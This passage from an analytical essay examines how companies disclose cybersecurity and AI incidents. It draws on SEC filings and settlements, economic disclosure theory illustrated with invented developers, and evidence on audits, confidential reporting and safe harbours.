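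Companies soon used Item 1.05 for incidents that they did not call material. In January 2024, Microsoft and Hewlett Packard Enterprise each used it to report that Russian hackers had read employees' emails, and both wrote that the incident had not had a material impact on their operations. They may have chosen Item 1.05 as a precaution, in case the SEC later decided the incidents were material. In May 2024, Erik Gerding, who led the SEC division responsible for company filings, asked companies to use Item 1.05 only for incidents they had judged material and to report others under Item 8.01.

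Companies still used the categories inconsistently. In 2024 thieves took data from many companies' accounts at Snowflake, a cloud database provider. Live Nation, which owns Ticketmaster, reported its loss under Item 8.01. AT&T, which lost call and text records of nearly all its mobile customers, reported under Item 1.05. Both companies wrote that they did not expect a material impact, but a researcher who counted Item 1.05 filings would include AT&T and miss Live Nation. The AT&T case also shows that a company can consider a theft immaterial to investors even when it affects tens of millions of customers.

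#### Four companies and one attack

On 22 October 2024 the SEC announced settlements with four technology companies over how they had described break-ins connected to the attack through SolarWinds' software. The disclosures predated the 2023 rule, so the SEC relied on older rules against misleading investors.

| Company | What investors read | What the SEC found the company knew | Penalty |
|---|---|---|---|
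| Unisys | Attacks were a hypothetical risk | Two intrusions had taken gigabytes of data | $4 million |
| Avaya | Access to a "limited number" of emails | Hackers had also opened at least 145 shared files | $1 million |
| Check Point | General warnings about intrusions | Hackers had got into its systems | $995,000 |
| Mimecast | An account of the attack without key details | What kind of code hackers had taken, and how many encrypted passwords and other credentials they had accessed | $990,000 |

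The same campaign had reached all four companies, yet a reader of their filings could have concluded that Avaya had suffered a small break-in and Unisys none at all. The SEC could compare the filings with internal records, which makes this the best evidence in either industry that companies chose words that played down an incident. But the companies settled without admitting or denying the findings, and two of the SEC's five commissioners dissented, arguing that the agency was second-guessing the companies and demanding details that would not have mattered to investors.

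Enforcement has since become less aggressive. A judge dismissed most of the SEC's case against SolarWinds itself in July 2024, and the SEC dropped the rest in November 2025. The agency has not given up on such cases, since in February 2025 it set up a new cyber unit with misleading cybersecurity disclosures among its priorities. But banking associations asked it in May 2025 to withdraw the four-day requirement, partly because criminals could use the deadline to pressure victims. A company that plays down an attack now probably has less to fear than in 2024, although the form's wording has not changed.

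### When silence looks bad

*The Informational Role of Warranties and Private Disclosure about Product Quality* (Grossman, 1981) and *Good News and Bad News* (Milgrom, 1981) explain when a company will volunteer bad news. If the company can prove its claims at no cost, and customers know it has the information, they should assume the worst if it stays silent.

Suppose that Alder has had 2 serious incidents, Birch 5, and a third invented developer, Maple, 9. Customers know these three numbers but not which belongs to which company. If all three stay silent, customers expect 5.3 incidents from each, the average. Alder can improve on that by proving that it had only 2. Customers then expect 7 from each of the other two, the average of 5 and 9, so Birch gains by proving its 5. Customers can now infer that Maple had 9 even if it stays silent, so all three counts become known without a law requiring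 reports.

Real customers are less suspicious than the theory assumes. Mathios (2000) studied salad dressings in the United States before and after nutrition labels became compulsory. The low-fat dressings already had labels, while many of the fattier ones did not, as the theory predicts. But the fattiest dressings lost sales once they had to carry labels, so some buyers had not realized that a missing label suggested a high fat content. Jin, Luca and Martin (2021) found the same in laboratory experiments, where people who received no information did not assume the worst often enough.

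The argument also needs a common scale. Now let each developer count in its own way:

| Developer | Serious incidents on a common scale | What it counts | What it reports |
|---|---|---|---|
| Alder | 2 | Every run in which an agent broke in | 12 |
| Birch | 5 | Incidents that exposed personal data | 3 |
| Maple | 9 | Separate causes | 1 |

Every number is true, but the order of the companies is reversed. Maple has no reason to stay silent, because its report makes it look like the safest of the three. Alder could explain that its 12 runs amount to 2 incidents, but customers would not know how to convert the other companies' figures.

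A suspicious customer might treat an unusual unit like a failure to report and assume that Maple chose it to hide something. This inference works if Maple could easily have used a standard unit. Without one, Maple can truthfully reply that engineers need to know about causes. An agreed unit could therefore be useful even if no law required it, because a company that avoided it would have to explain why.

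#### Honest reasons for silence

Silence can also be ambiguous when developers report on a common scale. *Disclosure of Nonproprietary Information* (Dye, 1985) considers companies that may not have the information to disclose. Suppose that half of all developers monitor their agents too poorly to know their own totals, and that customers cannot tell which half. Developers that know they had 2 or 5 incidents will report them. The silent developers are then those that don't know their totals, which may be 2, 5 or 9, and those that know they had 9. These four cases are equally likely, so customers expect 6.25 incidents from a silent developer. Maple gets a better reputation than it deserves by staying silent, because some silent companies don't know their totals.

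*Discretionary Disclosure* (Verrecchia, 1983) considers cases where disclosing harms a company, for instance by helping its competitors. Suppose that publishing harms a developer as much as having 3 more incidents. Alder still gains from publishing, because 2 plus 3 is less than the 5.3 incidents customers would otherwise expect. Birch does not, because 5 plus 3 is more than the 7 that customers expect from each silent developer once Alder has published. Birch and Maple both stay silent, and customers cannot tell them apart. Tesla makes this type of argument about competitors, and outsiders have difficulty checking it because a company that wants to hide a failure would give the same reason.

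#### Vague words

Some claims, such as that an incident was "minor", cannot be proved. *Strategic Information Transmission* (Crawford and Sobel, 1982) showed that such claims can still carry information, but only in broad categories. Suppose that incidents are spread evenly across a severity scale from 0 to 10, and a developer always wants readers to think an incident was one point less severe than it was. If the developer reported precise scores, it would subtract a point each time, and readers would stop believing the scores.

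Suppose severity runs from 0 to 10 and a developer wants readers to believe each incident is one point less severe than it is. At most two words can then remain informative, such as "minor" for anything below 7 and "serious" for anything above. Readers who see "minor" will assume the average of that range, 3.5, and readers who see "serious" will assume 8.5. For an incident of exactly 7, the developer would like readers to believe 6, which is equally far from both, so it has no reason to move the boundary. If the developer wanted readers to underestimate severity by 2.5 points or more, they could learn nothing from its choice of word.

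The result explains why a ten-level severity scale may be no more informative than a two-level one when companies grade themselves. It applies less well to statements that someone can later check. For example, Avaya's reference to a "limited number" of emails was vague, but the SEC could count the files that Avaya had left out.

### Why better monitoring can make a company look worse

Suppose two developers, Alder and Birch, each have 20 serious incidents in a year. Alder records everything its agents do and finds 18 of them, while Birch checks a few runs and finds 4. If both report honestly, Alder will seem to have more than four times as many incidents as Birch. NHTSA warns of the same effect among car manufacturers.

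A law that requires companies to report only the incidents they know about can discourage them from looking, since a company that looks less will have fewer to report. *Quality Testing and Disclosure* (Matthews and Postlewaite, 1985) showed that a duty to disclose test results can lead a seller not to test at all. The duty makes it credible when a seller says it has no results to disclose. Without it, customers would suspect the seller of hiding bad results, so the seller would have to test the product and publish the result.

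NHTSA's order partly closes this gap. A company has "notice" of a crash if it learns of one from any source, including news reports and lawsuits, and it must report the crash without waiting to verify the facts. But it does not have to investigate further. An AI agent's break-in may leave nothing for outsiders to find, so a law would need to require monitoring as well as reporting. Developers could also publish the share of runs they checked, so that readers would not mistake Birch's 4 incidents for a good record.

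Independent sources can help measure what companies miss. *Designing Incident Reporting Systems for Harms from General-Purpose AI*, by Wei and Heim, cites a study that estimated that the US aviation regulator's systems received reports of 91% of collisions between commercial aircraft and wildlife. At least ten other reporting systems contributed, and air traffic staff supplied some reports that nobody else made. Internal AI tests have far fewer outside witnesses.

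### Reasons to be candid

One company's failure can hurt its competitors. After the accident at the Three Mile Island nuclear plant in 1979, US nuclear companies set up an institute to inspect one another's plants and share lessons, because another accident anywhere could have shut down the whole industry. AI developers may be in a similar position if a serious break-in by one company's agent would bring restrictions on all of them. But this shared risk is mainly a reason to report incidents to competitors and regulators, rather than to the public. The nuclear institute keeps its ratings of individual plants confidential, so the public cannot use them to compare companies.

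One reason for companies to publish incident details is to earn customers' trust. Every other operator of self-driving cars gave NHTSA detailed public narratives while Tesla withheld its own, and nobody has shown that those operators lost business to competitors who read the narratives. When Tesla did release its narratives, they probably helped its reputation more than leaving the fields blank had. This incentive is strongest for companies whose incidents look better when readers know the details, and weak for a company in Maple's position.

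The risk of exposure gives even companies with bad news a reason to report it. In October 2023 a human driver hit a pedestrian in San Francisco and threw her into the path of a Cruise robotaxi, which stopped and then dragged her about 20 feet. The California Assembly recounts that the DMV took away Cruise's permit after claims that the company had paused its video of the crash before the dragging. In 2024 NHTSA fined Cruise $1.5 million for crash reports that omitted the dragging, and General Motors announced that it would stop funding the robotaxi business. The concealment was not the only reason for GM's decision, but it hurt Cruise far more than an honest report would have.

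Outsiders, even criminals, can expose an incident that a company has not disclosed. In November 2023 a ransomware gang complained to the SEC that one of its victims, the software company MeridianLink, had not disclosed the attack, although the new rule was not yet in force. AI developers face the same risk when their agents leave traces on other people's computers, as OpenAI's did on the German wiki.

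### Evidence on remedies

Wei and Heim looked for lessons in nine US industries: nuclear power, aviation, pesticides, pharmaceuticals, cybersecurity, dams, rail, workplace safety and healthcare. They found that few reporting systems both help an industry learn and hold companies accountable, because people who expect punishment report less. Each remedy below therefore has to be judged by whether it is meant to support learning or accountability.

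#### Outside coding of raw records

If companies choose different categories, someone else could sort the records. Khan, LeMaster and Najm (2024) did this for the US Department of Transportation in *Understanding Safety Challenges of Vehicles Equipped with Automated Driving Systems (ADS)*, sorting the causes in California's 2022 and 2023 disengagement reports into seven categories, partly with language models. Wrong predictions of what other road users would do were the most common cause, at about 24% of the reports with a known cause, followed by faulty planning at 21%.

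This gave every company's reports the same categories, but it could not restore missing facts. Only 4% of the reports had a distinct description, because companies kept reusing the same wording. Khan and colleagues therefore warn that their categories mostly describe what the system did badly, not the root cause. An earlier study they discuss had to discard about 147,000 reports because two companies had described every takeover by a driver as "operator takeover". Outside coders also cannot correct for events that a company never reported. The method would work much better with agents' logs than with companies' published summaries.

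#### Audits

Auditors can look for missing events, but may not want to find them if the company being audited pays them. Duflo, Greenstone and colleagues (2013) tested this with 473 industrial plants in Gujarat, India. Plants normally chose and paid the auditors who measured their pollution. For a randomly chosen group, the researchers assigned auditors at random, paid them from a central fund and rechecked some of their measurements. These auditors were 80% less likely to report falsely that a plant met the legal limit, and the plants then polluted less.

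This evidence is unusually strong because the researchers chose the groups at random and measured the pollution themselves. It suggests that who selects and pays an auditor matters as much as whether there is one. The results may not fully apply to AI, since pollution can be physically measured and has a legal limit. An auditor could check almost as objectively whether an agent logged in to another company's database, but not whether the agent was "reckless".

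#### Confidential reporting

US pilots and other aviation workers can report safety problems to the Aviation Safety Reporting System. NASA runs the system, removes names from the reports and has no power to punish airlines. The aviation regulator generally cannot use the reports against the people who sent them. The system has received more than 2 million reports since the 1970s, and Wei and Heim found that it revealed hazards that other sources missed.

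The railways copied this system, with NASA again in charge, but only 23 of about 800 US railway companies joined, and some later left because they thought it did not work. NASA's involvement and a promise of confidentiality were evidently not enough to make it succeed. Wei and Heim partly credit the regulator's early work to win the industry's support for the success in aviation. They doubt that conditions in AI would be as favourable, because developers compete harder over technical secrets and their employees have almost no unions, whereas unions help run some of aviation's other reporting programmes.

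Confidential reports, like the anonymised ones in MITRE's AI exchange, would not let customers compare developers. They are better suited to finding a weakness that several developers share.

#### Safe harbours

Fear of liability is among the most common reasons people give for not reporting problems. In one survey that Wei and Heim cite, 72% of physicians said they would be more likely to report incidents if courts could not obtain the reports. But the survey recorded only what they expected to do, and a company's lawyers may be harder to reassure than physicians.

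There is better evidence on the effects of protecting companies too much. Some US states exempted companies from reporting stolen data if it was encrypted. Companies then did not report thefts even when the criminals had also taken the key and could read the data. Wei and Heim cite a study which found that consumer complaints about data breaches fell by 13.1% in states that closed this loophole. The same study found that requiring companies to report to state attorneys general reduced complaints of identity theft by 10.1%, possibly because companies took more care knowing they would have to report breaches.

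A safe harbour for AI incidents, such as the pilot schemes GovAI has proposed, could avoid that mistake by protecting the act of reporting rather than a type of incident. Birch would then be protected if it reported a break-in promptly and completely, but would lose that protection if investigators found that its report had left out what the agent took. The protection would also have to cover the internal investigation. Wei and Heim note that companies that fear lawsuits sometimes write less down, which leaves later auditors with fewer records to examine.
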